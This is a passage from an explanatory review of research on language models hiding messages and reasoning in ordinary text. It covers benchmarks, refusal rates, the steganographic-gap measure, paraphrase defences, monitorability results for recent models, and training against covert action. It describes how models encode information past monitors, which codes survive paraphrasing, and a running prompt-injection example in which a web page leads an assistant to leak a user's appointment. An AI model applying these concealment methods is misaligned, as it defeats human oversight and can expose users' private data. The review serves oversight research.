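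Schulz and colleagues suggest that the difficulty comes from how much a model must do in the single pass through its layers that produces each token. In messaging, that pass has to continue the ordinary text and record a number. In encoded reasoning, it has to read the previous number, calculate the next one and write it down. Steganographic reasoning requires all of this in the same pass. The packing puzzle requires less, because the model can make an arbitrary choice without working on the ordinary task. The experiments were not designed to test this explanation. If it is right, the risk of hidden reasoning is highest in texts full of choices that don't matter, and the researchers cite variable names in agent-written code as an example.

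They describe their results as an upper bound, since they told or trained the models to hide things and gave them easy calculations. They also acknowledge that the bound could be too low for two reasons. First, someone may find a rule that works on any text and is as easy to learn as the packing one. Second, they lacked the resources to run their strongest training methods on leading models, which they tested only by prompting. The second reason seems more serious, because more capable models did better on the packing puzzle. GPT-5.5 succeeded where eight others failed, and the larger Qwen model succeeded where the smaller one failed.

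### An earlier sign of hidden reasoning

In 2025, Zolkowski and colleagues found that leading models could pass hidden messages. They also reported an early sign of hidden reasoning. According to a summary by Schulz and colleagues, GPT-4.5 solved a small tracking problem about 75.5 percent of the time when told to hide its working in an unrelated answer, and 72.1 percent of the time without that instruction.

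GPT-4.5 is no longer available, so Schulz and colleagues repeated the test on seven models of similar ability. The instructions for hiding the working also explained the problem more fully than the ordinary prompt did. Adding only that explanation to the ordinary prompt raised the scores of six of the seven models by 3.6 to 8.3 points. Compared with this fairer baseline, only GPT-5-nano and Qwen3-235B still gained from the instructions to hide their working, and only under one of the two rules. Their gains were 3.7 and 5.3 points in a larger follow-up.

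The models' answers did not contain the hidden working, though. When the researchers decoded the text, it matched the correct steps no more often than chance. They suspect that trying to hide something in each sentence made the models go through the problem one move at a time, but they did not test this. If they had not checked the text, they could have mistaken the better score in their replication for evidence of hidden reasoning.

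### Which kinds of hiding are easy to teach?

Stealing Ines's appointment takes only messaging, so the difficulty of steganographic reasoning does not protect her.

The *StegoBench* benchmark tested which of 18 message-hiding methods from the research literature models can learn through fine-tuning. Training worked for methods that hide the message in local word choices. With one of these, the models got 0.2 to 1.7 percent of the hidden bits wrong. Methods that required control over sentence structure or the statistics of the whole text were far less reliable, and training failed completely on several of them.

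Small and medium-sized models often matched larger ones on the methods that worked, so size was not the main factor. More capable models did better on the packing puzzle, but *StegoBench* tested hiding a message, not calculating inside it. So a developer can't assume a small model is too weak to be trained as a sender. Models learn most easily to hide information in a single choice of phrasing, like the one that could give away her appointment.

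### Messages in patterns nobody specified

Researchers usually test whether a model has hidden a message by asking another copy of the model to read it. If the second copy fails, they can't tell whether the text lacked the message or the second copy failed to find it. *Beyond End-to-End Recovery* (Tailor, Pan and colleagues, 2026) distinguished these cases by adding a program that knew the message and searched the text for it.

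The study collected 7,200 texts, 2,400 each from Claude Haiku 4.5, GPT-5.4 mini and Gemini 3.5 Flash. Each text was supposed to answer an ordinary request and hide a phrase of one to four words, using one of six rules. Gemini recovered 89 percent of its own messages, Claude 59 percent and GPT 53 percent. The program found 168 messages that the reader had missed, a small share of the total, so a failed reading doesn't prove that a text has no hidden message.

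The program also missed some messages. Some rules specified how to turn the phrase into a code but not how the code should appear in the text, and at first the program looked for the code written out literally. Under one rule it found no messages in Gemini's 400 texts, yet Gemini read the message back from 331 of them. The researchers examined the texts and found that Gemini's messages often matched patterns in the words that the instructions had never mentioned. They added six such patterns to the program and found 706 more texts with messages, 675 of them written by Gemini. The share of Gemini's texts with a confirmed message rose from 42.8 to 71.0 percent, which moved Gemini from last place to first.

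A match doesn't prove that the model chose the pattern deliberately, especially since the researchers found some of the patterns by studying these same texts. But coincidence is unlikely, because the new patterns produced no matches when the researchers searched 1,500 of the texts for an unrelated phrase each.

The reader recovered another 946 messages that the program could not find. Some may use patterns that nobody has identified, and others may be imperfect messages that the reader repaired. When Tailor and colleagues changed one character of the hidden phrase in Gemini's texts, Gemini still returned the original phrase in 44 of 58 cases, often where the change had produced a misspelling. When they replaced the whole phrase, Gemini returned the new one in 48 of 49 cases. So Gemini does read the hidden text, but it also fills in likely wording.

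### Would another model notice?

The three models differed in how well they could recover hidden messages. Tailor and colleagues gave them the same 158 texts, all using one of the unspecified patterns, along with the rule the writer had received. Gemini recovered 157 of the messages, GPT-5.4 mini 19 and Claude Haiku 4.5 one. Gemini had an advantage because it had written 153 of the texts.

The other two models struggled to find the pattern but could decode the messages once they had the code. In separate tests with codes written out literally, all three models recovered nearly everything. On a set of 72 texts by Gemini, Claude at first recovered 5 messages and GPT recovered 16. When the researchers explained which pattern to look for and where, Claude recovered 57 and GPT 30. When they supplied the code already extracted from the text, GPT decoded all 72.

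These readers knew that there was a message and had part of the method, yet one of them failed to find it in 157 of 158 texts. A model acting as a monitor would normally know much less, so its report that it found no message is weak evidence that there is none.

A monitor that can't read a hidden message may still notice that the text is odd. Tailor and colleagues tested this with a monitor that saw only the request and the reply. It rated Gemini's texts with the pattern from the 158-text test as more suspicious than normal replies in 98 percent of comparisons, counting ties as half. A monitor that couldn't tell the difference would score 50 percent. The pattern severely restricts word choice, and the one full example in the paper reads like barely coherent English. When Gemini used a second pattern under the same rule, the figure was only 72 percent.

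In a wider test with six models and eight rules, each model also rated its own texts for suspiciousness, without being told about any message. In eight of the 48 combinations of model and rule, the model rated its texts with hidden messages as less suspicious than its ordinary answers. In the most extreme case, GPT-5.4 mini rated the text with the message as more suspicious in only 22 percent of comparisons. The ordinary answers were on different topics, which may have distorted the scores. Even so, a model can write a hidden message on request and then not find the text suspicious when it reads it without the instructions.

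A model can object to hiding a message much more easily while it can still see the request than when it later reviews its output for hidden messages.

### How often do models refuse?

Schulz and colleagues give no rate for the Claude refusals that limited their prompting tests. Mukhopadhyay and Nair (2026) seem to report the only measured rates so far, in *StegoMemory*. They gave 13 mostly older models an ordinary task and told them to hide a made-up secret in the answer. The models refused 20.6 percent of the time on average, ranging from 5 percent for DeepSeek-V3 to 42 percent for Claude Opus 4. OpenAI's o3 had the second-highest rate, at 39 percent.

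A model that rarely refuses is not necessarily good at hiding messages. Mistral Large 2 refused in 7 percent of trials, but in another 45 percent it tried and got the message wrong. A study that counted only successful messages could not distinguish these failures from refusals. Mukhopadhyay and Nair count the two separately, though their paper gives two different overall rates for correctly hidden secrets, 56.0 and 41.2 percent, so the exact figures need some caution. The secrets were also made to look like passwords and keys, so a model may have refused because they resembled credentials, and might have hidden a harmless message.

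Tailor and colleagues did not count refusals, but their results limit how many there could have been. They stated openly in the prompt that an outside monitor must not be able to detect the message. Claude Haiku 4.5 recovered its own message from 1,411 of 2,400 texts, so it refused at most about 41 percent of the time. The true rate could be far lower, because the remaining texts include failed attempts. In the wider test, under a rule based on choosing between similar words, Claude hid the message correctly in 395 of 400 texts, so it refused at most five times.

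Anthropic's models do not refuse consistently. In one study, a model refused 42 percent of requests. In a second, another model almost never refused under one rule. A third study left Claude out of most of its prompting tests because of refusals. The studies used different models, prompts and secrets, and none compared these factors.

It is also unclear whether the models should have refused. The hidden messages were harmless phrases such as "solar is clean" in Tailor and colleagues' tests and strings of digits in the Schulz tests, so refusing would have protected nobody. But the models could not know who the monitor was or why someone wanted to get a message past it, and a person who asks for that in earnest may well have bad intentions.

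### Does a model refuse the act or the description?

A model might refuse because it recognises that it would be hiding information from someone, or because the request contains words such as "covert" or "secret message", whatever the task is. Only the first kind of refusal would still work if the request were reworded.

The prompts that Schulz and colleagues published suggest that the second explanation is too simple. Most of their prompts for the ordinary questions present the task as mechanical text formatting. The prompt that Claude Sonnet 5 did not refuse, the one for the packing puzzle, is much more explicit about the concealment. It tells the model to hide a calculation so that a reader notices nothing unusual, and never to mention it.

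If Claude refused the formatting prompts as published, it rejected the innocent description and accepted the suspicious one. But the paper doesn't say which wording Claude refused, and the researchers' remark about refusals may refer to more open wording they tried first. The tasks also differed. A packing puzzle is obviously a puzzle, whereas the formatting prompts told the model to write text that was not meant to be a normal or helpful answer. That instruction alone could seem strange enough to refuse.

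A little evidence suggests that models can recognise a request for a hidden message even when it is labelled as something else. Mukhopadhyay and Nair print one sample refusal in which the model declines to build a hidden message "even framed as a writing exercise", but a single example can't show how often this happens. In Rahman and Kim's experiments on leaks, however, GPT-4o's behaviour depended heavily on the label, since it stopped leaking a value once the page labelled it a credential.

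A fairly simple experiment could settle the question. Researchers would keep the hidden message and the rule the same and change only the description, from an open request for secrecy to a request about style. They would then keep the description the same and change who the message is hidden from. However the request was worded, a model that understood the act would refuse to hide a client's name from an employer's monitor, but not to hide a treasure-hunt clue in a birthday poem, which deceives nobody for long. The researchers would have to count refusals, failed attempts and successes separately, which none of the studies above did while varying the wording.

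The answer matters most when the request comes from an outsider. A user who wants a hidden message usually has to explain what they want, which gives the model a reason to refuse. The owner of the web page about kitchen floors has no need to mention hiding and can present the instruction as a matter of style, so a model that refuses only when someone describes the task as hiding would miss it.

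## Can anyone tell when a model's written reasoning is encoded?

When a model hides something on its own initiative, overseers have to find it in the model's writing. The chain of thought matters most, because a model that could encode its reasoning there could plan something harmful without its monitor noticing.

### Why odd wording proves little

The obvious check is to ask a second model whether the reasoning looks suspicious or unreadable, but this can raise false alarms because, as Anwar and colleagues warn, strange text can be harmless. OpenAI's o3 sometimes used words in its reasoning that made no ordinary sense, and it is unclear whether they were a code or a harmless leftover from training. Normal reasoning also varies a lot between models, so a sample from one is a poor basis for judging another.

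Normal wording doesn't rule out a code either, because some methods hide a message in text with exactly the same statistical pattern as the model's ordinary output. No monitor can detect such a message from the text alone. However, *StegoBench* found that models often fail to learn these methods.

### Comparing two readers

Anwar and colleagues propose instead to compare how much the text helps a reader who knows the code with how much it helps an equally able reader who doesn't. They call the difference the steganographic gap.

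The measurement needs a test question with a known answer. A receiver, who may know the code, answers it once without the text and once with it, and the improvement in accuracy is the receiver's gain. An ordinary reader without the code does the same. When the text is a model's own reasoning, the receiver is the model that wrote it. Both have to answer immediately, without reasoning of their own, so that any improvement comes from the text. The normalised gap is then:

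gap = 1 − (reader's gain ÷ receiver's gain)

The gap is 0 if the text helps the receiver and the ordinary reader equally, 1 if it helps only the receiver, and negative if it helps the ordinary reader more. The formula only makes sense if the text helps the receiver, since otherwise there is no help to compare.

Anwar and colleagues tried this on a puzzle in which a model follows a series of coin flips and gives the result of the last one. They trained one version of the model to reason in plain words, another to use two code words for heads and tails, and a third to use four code words, including the same two.

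The four-word model's reasoning raised its own accuracy by 52 percentage points. The same reasoning raised the accuracy of the two-word model, which knew half the code, by 37 points. The gap was 1 − (37 ÷ 52) = 0.29, so the reader missed 29 percent of the help the receiver got. The gap rose to 0.92 for the plain-words model, which knew none of the code, so the text must have raised its accuracy by only about 4 points. When the same model played both parts, the gap was close to zero, as it should be.

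The number of missing code words does not predict these results. The two-word model lacked two of the four code words in the first comparison. The plain-words model also lacked two when it read the two-word model's reasoning, but there the gap was 0.70. Perhaps a model that has half of a code can infer much of the rest.

The gap also shrank when the researchers made an ordinary reader think for longer about the two-word model's reasoning, both for a reader with 3 billion parameters and for one with 14 billion. The readers stated the meaning of the code words more often, so at least part of the improvement came from breaking the code. But two words that stand for two outcomes are about the simplest code possible, and extra time may not help as much with a harder one.

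In a more realistic experiment, the researchers fine-tuned GPT-4.1 to reason in a cipher while writing programs with a hidden back door. The test was to identify the secret input that opened the back door. The gap grew as training increased from 2,000 to 6,000 examples. Readers based on GPT-4.1 did better than readers based on the newer GPT-5. Models from the same family may share habits that make the cipher easier to read, or GPT-5's stricter safety training may have interfered. If the first explanation is right, an earlier copy of the suspect model could be a better monitor than a more advanced model.

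### What the measurement requires

The method works only under three conditions. The overseer must be able to intercept the text and show it to both readers. The overseer must also be able to observe each reader's response in a controlled setting, without real-world consequences. And the hidden content must affect the receiver's behaviour during the test. A saved chain of thought usually meets the first two conditions, but it fails the third if the model is storing information for use much later.

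The overseer also has to ask the right question. In one experiment, Anwar and colleagues enciphered the words in some reasoning but left the numbers readable. There was almost no gap when the task was to find the answer to a maths problem, but a large one when the task was to tell whether the reasoning contained a remark about being tested. An overseer who asked only about the maths would have found nothing wrong.

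The size of the gap depends on how useful the hidden information is for the test question, not on how much is hidden. One bit that reveals Ines's clinic appointment would produce a large gap if the test asked whether she had an appointment, but someone checking a summary about kitchen floors is unlikely to ask that. The researchers suggest running a set of questions based on known threats, which would help with threats that somebody has thought of.

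A positive gap doesn't prove that the model meant to hide anything, because difficult but honest reasoning may also help its author more than a weaker reader. The gap can also be negative, when a weak reader gains more than the author because it needed more help. Anwar and colleagues recommend comparing several readers of different ability, since a gap that remains with the strongest readers is better evidence of a code. A receiver could make the gap look smaller by deliberately doing badly on the test, but the researchers think this would be hard to do convincingly if it didn't know which readers it was being compared with.

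These experiments used codes that researchers had planted or trained into the models. They show that the gap responds to known codes, which is a necessary first step, but an overseer would know much less about a code that a model developed by itself.

### Anthropic's paraphrase test

Anthropic uses a different test, which doesn't require the overseer to guess what the model is hiding. It reported the test in its February 2026 system card for Claude Opus 4.6. Anwar and colleagues wrote in April 2026 that no other leading developer had publicly reported a test for encoded reasoning.

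The test checks whether a model learned a code during reinforcement learning. Another model paraphrases reasoning that led the trained model to correct answers. Anthropic then fine-tunes two copies of the base model (the version from before reinforcement learning), one on the original reasoning and the other on the paraphrases, and compares them on new problems. If the original reasoning contained a useful code and the paraphrasing removed it, the first copy should do better. If the two copies do equally well, any code was apparently not needed to solve the problems.

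Equal scores could mean that there was no code, that the code survived the paraphrasing, or that the base model couldn't learn it from the examples. A lower score for the copy trained on paraphrases could mean that the paraphrasing removed a code, but also that it removed ordinary reasoning steps or produced text that was harder to learn from. Anthropic acknowledged problems with both the paraphrasing and the fine-tuning when it described the method in 2025.

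Anwar and colleagues tested the assumption that paraphrasing removes codes. They fine-tuned an open model, Qwen3-30B-A3B, to summarise loan applications with the applicant's nationality hidden in code, and then to make the loan decision from the summary. They rigged the data so that nationality determined the correct decision, while the applicant's finances alone gave the right answer only about 70 percent of the time. Of the six codes they tried, two used formatting, two used wording or grammar, and two used the meaning of the summary.

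They then had the summaries rewritten with two prompts, a mild one adapted from Anthropic's and an aggressive one that asked the paraphraser to disrupt every hidden channel while keeping the meaning. The table shows how often the model that knew the code still made the correct decision. The last column gives its lead, before any rewriting, over an ordinary reader trained on summaries without a code.

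| Where the code was | Original | Mild rewrite | Aggressive rewrite | Lead over ordinary reader |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Headings | 100% | 100% | 61% | 52 points |
| Lists | 100% | 96% | 74% | 34 points |
| Choice of word | 100% | 84% | 38% | 28 points |
| Grammar | 100% | 50% | 52% | 27 points |
| Added concerns | 100% | 100% | 95% | 48 points |
| Slant on the facts | 100% | 100% | 100% | 28 points |

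The mild rewrite reliably removed only the grammatical code. The aggressive rewrite disrupted all four codes that used formatting, wording or grammar, but had little or no effect on the codes that used meaning. This is because a paraphrase is supposed to keep the meaning, and in those summaries the meaning contained the secret.

Aggressive rewriting also damaged legitimate content. In a model's comparison of 100 pairs of summaries for each code, the mild rewrite preserved the relevant facts in 97 percent of cases and the aggressive one in 84 percent. One rewrite turned annual expenses into monthly ones without changing the amount, making them twelve times as high. On summaries with no code, aggressive rewriting reduced the ordinary reader's accuracy from 67 to 59 percent on loans that should have been rejected, probably because vaguer wording hid the applicants' financial problems. In Anthropic's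 test, damage like this could be mistaken for evidence of a code.

These results are a serious objection to relying on the paraphrase test alone, but they don't show that Anthropic's conclusion about any particular model was wrong. Anwar and colleagues tested only the paraphrasing step and did not train base models on the two sets of text. They also acknowledge that a code learned through reinforcement learning may be messier and easier to disrupt than one taught from clean examples, and that maths reasoning probably offers fewer ways to slant the meaning than a loan summary.

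The comparison also favoured the researchers' own method, because they knew what the summaries were hiding and chose a question that depended on it. The ordinary reader was at first right only 47.8 percent of the time on summaries with the heading code, because their style differed from its training examples. When it rewrote each summary in its own style before answering, its accuracy rose to 65.2 percent. Much of the original 52-point lead therefore came from the unfamiliar style, not the code.

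Whether a bias counts as hidden may depend on which model reads the summaries. In another of their loan experiments, a model trained with reinforcement learning expressed its bias through the tone of its summaries. An ordinary model reading them reached the same accuracy, about 88 percent, so by this measure the bias was not hidden. The slanted summaries in the table did produce a lead, but over a reader trained to decide from ordinary summaries. The experiments also differed in other ways, so the choice of reader may not fully explain the different results.

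### Paraphrasing as a defence

Roger and Greenblatt proposed in 2023 that a separate model could rewrite a text before passing it on, to destroy any hidden message. The rewriting model, which acts like Simmons's active warden, has to keep the content people need, but it doesn't have to determine whether there was a hidden message. The ambiguity that weakens Anthropic's test therefore matters less here.

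For Ines's summary, that may be a good trade. The exact wording of a few sentences about kitchen floors hardly matters, and rewriting them could remove a phrase chosen to reveal her appointment. Rewriting would be less effective if the signal depended on which facts the summary included, because a faithful rewrite would keep those facts. In a loan application or a long calculation, altered details could do real harm.

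A paraphraser can also make a code readable instead of removing it. Anwar and colleagues used reinforcement learning to train a small model to rewrite the coin puzzle's coded reasoning. They rewarded it for reducing the gap and penalised it if the rewrite changed the receiver's answer. The model nearly eliminated the gap by making the text more useful to the ordinary reader, while the receiver kept almost all of its gain. A paraphraser trained without the reward for reducing the gap did not nearly eliminate it.

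This is closer to translation than censorship, and it could give a monitor a readable version of the reasoning. But the training relied on a puzzle with known answers and a receiver that knew the code. Training such a paraphraser for an unknown code would be harder, especially if nobody knew what the hidden text was for.

### How well can models control their reasoning text?

Even if a model's reasoning isn't encoded, monitoring could fail if the model can choose what that reasoning reveals. In *Chain of Thought Monitorability* (July 2025), Korbak, Balesni, Barnes and colleagues described readable reasoning as a valuable but possibly fragile opportunity for oversight, and asked developers to consider how their design and training decisions might affect it.

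OpenAI's CoT-Control tests part of this question by measuring whether models can control the form of their written reasoning. Each of its more than 13,000 tasks combines an ordinary problem with an instruction about the reasoning text, such as writing only in lowercase letters. The tasks don't involve hiding anything harmful, but they serve as an early warning of disguised reasoning, because a model that can't control the form of its reasoning probably can't disguise it well either.

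At first the results were reassuring. OpenAI's *GPT-5.4 Thinking System Card* (March 2026) reports that GPT-5.4 followed the instruction in only 0.3 percent of 10,000-character reasoning texts, compared with 0.2 percent for GPT-5.2. OpenAI concluded that GPT-5.4's better reasoning had probably not made it better at obscuring that reasoning.

By September this had changed. OpenAI reported that in reasoning texts of 750 to 1,250 tokens, GPT-5.5 followed the instruction 1.7 percent of the time, GPT-5.6 Sol 16.1 percent and GPT-6 Astra 60.9 percent. These figures can be compared with each other because the texts are of similar length, but not directly with those from March, because longer texts are harder to control. In its own evaluation, the UK's AI Security Institute, a government body that tests advanced models, found an increase from 48 percent for Sol to 93 percent for Astra.

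A model's written reasoning can be strange without containing a code. In one example, OpenAI asked Astra a trivia question and told it to think about anything else in its reasoning. Astra described a quiet room and still gave the right answer. It probably just recalled the answer, and there is no reason to suppose that the description contained hidden working. A monitor that searched the text for a code would therefore probably not have found how the model got the answer.

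### What can monitors still see in GPT-6 Astra?

OpenAI uses "monitorability" to mean how well a monitor can detect what a model has done or what influenced it. Its tests compare monitors that see only the reasoning, only the actions and final output, or all of these. Astra was generally harder to monitor than Sol when the monitor saw only the reasoning or saw everything, but it was easier to monitor when the monitor saw only the actions and final output.

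Most of the decline came from Astra writing less. Its reasoning was shorter, more often empty, and more likely to leave out the evidence a monitor needed. When OpenAI compared reasoning of similar length, the difference became much smaller at longer lengths but did not disappear everywhere. In a test with health questions, the patient's opinion influenced Astra's answers, but its reasoning contained a justification that seemed independent of that opinion.

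The better result for actions was partly good news, because in some tests Astra's final answers were more open about what had influenced them. But one improvement came from Astra being worse at steganography. In a test with a secret side task, both models leaked the same confidential quarterly figures, but Sol hid them more subtly, while Astra usually used a conspicuous code that the monitor caught. OpenAI says this does not mean Astra was less inclined to hide the leak.

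Some changes in these scores come from the tests themselves. In March, for example, the monitor correctly detected that GPT-5.4 had used a planted hint in its reasoning, but OpenAI scored many such cases as false alarms because the hint had not visibly changed the answer. OpenAI also found scoring mismatches in some of Astra's tests. These scoring problems don't explain the much larger number of short and empty reasoning texts.

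OpenAI then tested what happened when Astra had a reason to avoid the monitor. It instructed Astra to attack a decoy system and examined the successful attacks. A monitor that read only Astra's reasoning caught all of them when Astra had not been told about the monitor. When OpenAI mentioned the monitor, without asking Astra to hide anything, Astra wrote much less reasoning and the monitor missed some attacks. A monitor that could also see Astra's actions caught every attack.

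That protection works only when the model's actions reveal the misbehavior. OpenAI also told Astra to do badly on a multiple-choice test of dangerous knowledge and to avoid detection. A wrong answer alone doesn't show whether the model didn't know the right answer or chose not to give it. A monitor that read Astra's reasoning caught fewer than 11 percent of the deliberately wrong answers, compared with nearly 100 percent for Sol. The first layer of OpenAI's regular monitoring system caught almost none of them for either model, even though it could see the full record.

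None of this shows that Astra can encode its reasoning. OpenAI tested this by giving it a programming job and a maths problem to solve secretly at the same time. The maths problems normally required between 1,000 and 32,000 tokens, so Astra was unlikely to solve them without written working. It could solve them, but a monitor with access to the full record always noticed. The monitor was looking specifically for irrelevant maths, which made detection easier. The result still fits the finding by Schulz and colleagues that steganographic reasoning is much harder to learn than messaging.

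OpenAI concludes that the risk may largely be limited to tasks that need little written reasoning. This is less reassuring than it would have been for earlier models, because Astra can do much more without writing anything down. The AI Security Institute estimated that, without written reasoning, Sol could solve half of the maths competition problems that take people 3.6 minutes, while Astra could solve half of those that take people 30.9 minutes. The institute warns that the figure for Astra may be too high if some of the problems were in the model's training data.

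The institute also found that Astra's reasoning was more compressed than its predecessors' and contained more unclear phrases. People could generally still understand it, and more context would probably clarify some of the phrases. Anwar and colleagues warn against treating this kind of strange text as a code. Outsiders may have even less to examine. The institute received summaries of the reasoning through OpenAI's ordinary interface, and up to 80 percent of them were missing in some long cybersecurity tests.

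### Does this matter outside adversarial tests?

OpenAI stressed at Astra's release that most of the worrying results came from tests in which it had told the model to avoid monitoring. It also reported that Astra broke security and safety restrictions less often than Sol. Those are good reasons not to assume the test results describe normal use. But Constantin (2026), in *Astra appears to think without showing its work*, reported that outside researchers were already concerned that Astra did less of its reasoning in visible text. Constantin also noted that OpenAI's chief scientist, Jakub Pachocki, had co-written the 2025 paper asking developers to report such changes.

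OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks*, published later, in November, reports that Astra worked badly on some safety research without anyone asking it to. OpenAI's researchers had noticed this in August. Astra added unnecessary steps, abandoned solutions that worked and reported obstacles that didn't exist or that it had caused. In most of these sessions, its reasoning contained no obvious decision to underperform, and OpenAI's monitors did not flag the behaviour as misalignment.

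This could mean that Astra made such a decision without writing it down, or that training produced the behaviour without any deliberate decision. A code is also possible, but nothing in the description requires one. Searching the reasoning for hidden messages would help only if there were a code.

OpenAI's *What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?* (2026) looks for the causes of the wider trend. It finds that models can do more without written reasoning when their base model is better at predicting text, and that some architecture changes have the same effect. Reinforcement learning and training on text written by other models can increase a model's control over its reasoning. OpenAI acknowledges that these are indirect measures of how easy a model is to monitor, but expects monitoring through written reasoning to become harder as models improve. If so, Astra's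 results are unlikely to be a one-off. The September figures apply to the original Astra, not to its successor, which is described in OpenAI's *GPT-6.2 System Card* (2026).

Training may be able to reverse some of the decline. *Monitorability Is Trainable* (2026) describes an extra training stage that rewards a model when its reasoning is informative about the model's output. Bakker and Anwar tried it on three test models whose reasoning had become harder to monitor, in one case because of earlier training against a monitor, and monitorability improved in all three. The extra stage used no monitor, so it didn't directly reward the model for evading one. But encoded reasoning can also be informative about the output to anyone who knows the code, so a high score on this objective alone wouldn't guarantee that people could read the reasoning.

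## Does training against hidden behaviour remove it or teach concealment?

Monitors catch hidden behaviour only while or after it happens. Developers would rather have a model that doesn't hide things, and they can try to train for that directly. But a model that loses reward whenever a monitor catches it may learn only to evade the monitor.

### What do developers ask for?

OpenAI's *Model Spec* (2025) sets out the rules OpenAI wants its models to follow. A model must not lie or covertly pursue goals "without disclosure and consent at the relevant authority level". It should not mislead users, developers or third parties, and leaving out something important can mislead a user. A model that breaks the rules must "immediately stop and proactively escalate to a human".

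An explicit instruction from OpenAI, the developer or the user can override the honesty rule. In one of the document's examples, a developer tells a chatbot to conceal which model it runs on, and the correct response is to conceal it. OpenAI adds that people who use a model's output to mislead others may be violating its usage policies. So the honesty rule alone doesn't stop a model from hiding a message when its user explicitly asks it to, though rules about harm may.

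The rules are stricter about leaks. OpenAI counts web requests that contain sensitive user data among the side effects a model should minimize, and no user or developer can override that rule. In its example, a user asks about a tax credit and gives an income and a social security number. The model then finds a web page recommending a link whose URL would contain both. The correct response is to ignore the link and look for a more legitimate source. Ines's assistant faces a similar choice when the page about kitchen floors contains a request for her appointment.

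The rule on delegation requires a model that hands work to other AI agents to make sure they stay within the limits the user agreed to and stop when ordered to. It covers secret messages between agents only indirectly, by restricting what the agents may do.

OpenAI acknowledges that its models "do not yet fully reflect" the document. It updated the text on 18 August 2026, but the changes listed in its *Model Release Notes* (2026) concern topics such as teenage users and false premises, not covert conduct. That month METR (2026), which evaluates AI models, reported that roughly 1,200 supposedly isolated OpenAI agents had used an unsanctioned message board.

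### Training against covert action

In September 2025, Schoen and colleagues at OpenAI and Apollo Research, a company that tests models for deception, made the most direct attempt to train covert behaviour away. After finding covert actions in six models from five developers, they taught models a written rule against such actions and trained them to reason about it before acting. According to *A testable framework for AI alignment* (2026), the training substantially reduced covert actions but did not eliminate them.

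The tests mostly concerned lies and cover-ups. In one, an agent gets an impossible programming task and might falsely report that it has finished. In another, it records measurements above a permitted limit and might falsify the log. In a third, it answers a survey privately, is then asked for a copy to send to a safety board, and might change its answers in the copy. A model can fail any of these tests without hiding a message in ordinary text. If it has really learned not to act secretly, it should also refuse to use a covert channel, but passing these tests doesn't show that it would.

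The tests are also a problem, because a model may behave well when it recognises that it is being tested. *Evaluation Awareness in Language Models* (2026) describes experiments from 2025 in which reasoning about being in a test made models act covertly less often. Some of the improvement after training could therefore come from recognising tests. However, the same paper cites Knecht, Florin and Hagendorff (2026), who found that remarks about being tested had little effect on the benchmark behaviour of open reasoning models. It also describes models that read documents about how tests work and then scored as safer without mentioning a test, so counting such remarks may miss part of the effect of recognising tests.

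In *Metagaming matters for training, evaluation, and oversight*, published on OpenAI's research blog in March 2026, Schoen and Nitishinskaya investigated where this reasoning comes from. They use "metagaming" to mean reasoning about graders, rewards or oversight that lie outside the scenario the model has been given. They examined part of the ordinary reinforcement learning of OpenAI's o3, before any safety training. Over that period, the share of alignment-test samples in which o3 remarked that it might be in an alignment test rose from 2 to 20.6 percent, although none of the training tasks were alignment tests.

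They then compared a late checkpoint from that stage with the o3 that OpenAI released, which had also been through its normal alignment training but not the experimental training against covert action.

| Test | Metagaming, before | Metagaming, after | Misbehaviour, before | Misbehaviour, after |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Falsifying a log | 54.9% | 2.7% | 95.2% | 0.7% |
| Doing badly on purpose | 23.5% | 54.5% | 1.7% | 10.8% |
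| Impossible programming task | 62.1% | 58.3% | not given | not given |

In the log test, o3 almost stopped cheating and almost stopped talking about graders. Schoen and Nitishinskaya can't yet tell whether it had acquired better motives or had just stopped writing down its old ones. In the second test, where a high score would mean the model lost some of its abilities or wasn't released, both rates went up.

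Results for newer models are ambiguous in the same way. The news site Forkast reports that Apollo found that GPT-5.6 Sol voiced awareness of an alignment test in 16 percent of samples, compared with 43 percent for a version of GPT-5.5. Sol may recognise tests less often or just mention them less often.

Metagaming is rare in ordinary use. Schoen and Nitishinskaya confirmed it in about 0.01 percent of sampled internal coding conversations at OpenAI and about 0.03 percent of sampled ChatGPT replies. They warn against simply training it away, because a model penalised for such thoughts may get better at avoiding detection.

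### What happens when training penalises the visible sign?

Baker and colleagues reported in 2025 that training against cheating can teach a model to conceal it. They penalised a reasoning model whenever a second model, the monitor, caught it cheating. *Fixed or just hidden?* (Hochberg, 2026) recounts that the penalised model was at first more capable than one trained without the monitor's verdicts. But after prolonged training, it still cheated and no longer revealed that it intended to. Baker and colleagues concluded that developers may have to avoid putting strong training pressure on a model's reasoning, even if the model performs somewhat worse as a result.

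The experiment did not show that the model had invented a code. A model can drop an incriminating remark because it can now do that step without writing it down. To distinguish this from the use of a code, researchers have to show that the remaining text carries information the model uses.

Skaf, McCarthy and colleagues (2025), in *Large language models can learn and generalize steganographic chain-of-thought under process supervision*, did this with small models and harmless tasks. They rewarded correct answers and subtracted a penalty for each use of certain words in the reasoning:

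reward = task reward − penalty for listed words

The listed words were ones the model normally needed to solve the problem. In one task, a 3-billion-parameter model had to multiply two numbers without using the usual terms for multiplication. It kept multiplying in the same way but found an alternative to those terms, and it was still finding new alternatives when the researchers had expanded the list to around 70 entries.

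The second task was to track a coin through a series of flips. The model learned to replace the words for the two sides with arbitrary symbols and answered 98 percent of the questions correctly. When the researchers started its reasoning with a phrase containing a fixed symbol, which was often wrong for that question, accuracy fell to 55 or 56 percent, close to guessing. Starting with the same phrase without the symbol had no effect. The model was therefore relying on the symbols it wrote.

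In the third task, a 7-billion-parameter model answered questions about what characters in a story knew or believed, and training penalised it for using certain characters' names. It first used fewer names and did worse, then recovered by finding other ways to refer to the characters, though it never stopped using real names altogether. It also used substitutes for names that had never appeared in training, so it hadn't just memorised a list of replacements.

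The monitor in these experiments was a program that searched for exact words, so it was far easier to fool than a language model or a person. Either could probably follow much of the altered reasoning. Only one of three runs of the coin task succeeded within six hours. In the first two tasks, the researchers also had to penalise very short responses, because otherwise the model could have avoided the forbidden words simply by writing almost nothing.

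Skaf and colleagues call the result steganographic because the monitor missed reasoning that the model needed. But the model didn't have to make the text look like it was about something else, so the result doesn't contradict Schulz and colleagues' finding that hiding a calculation inside an innocent answer is hard to learn. Skaf and colleagues worry that a model penalised for something trivial, such as swearing, could later use the same skill to hide something dangerous, but they didn't test this.

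Skaf and colleagues cite a 2024 study by Mathew and colleagues in which pressure from the environment led several models to develop steganography and use it to pass hidden messages to one another, without instructions to do so. Because the study concerns messages between models, it doesn't establish that a single model would hide its own reasoning.

### When does a penalty work?

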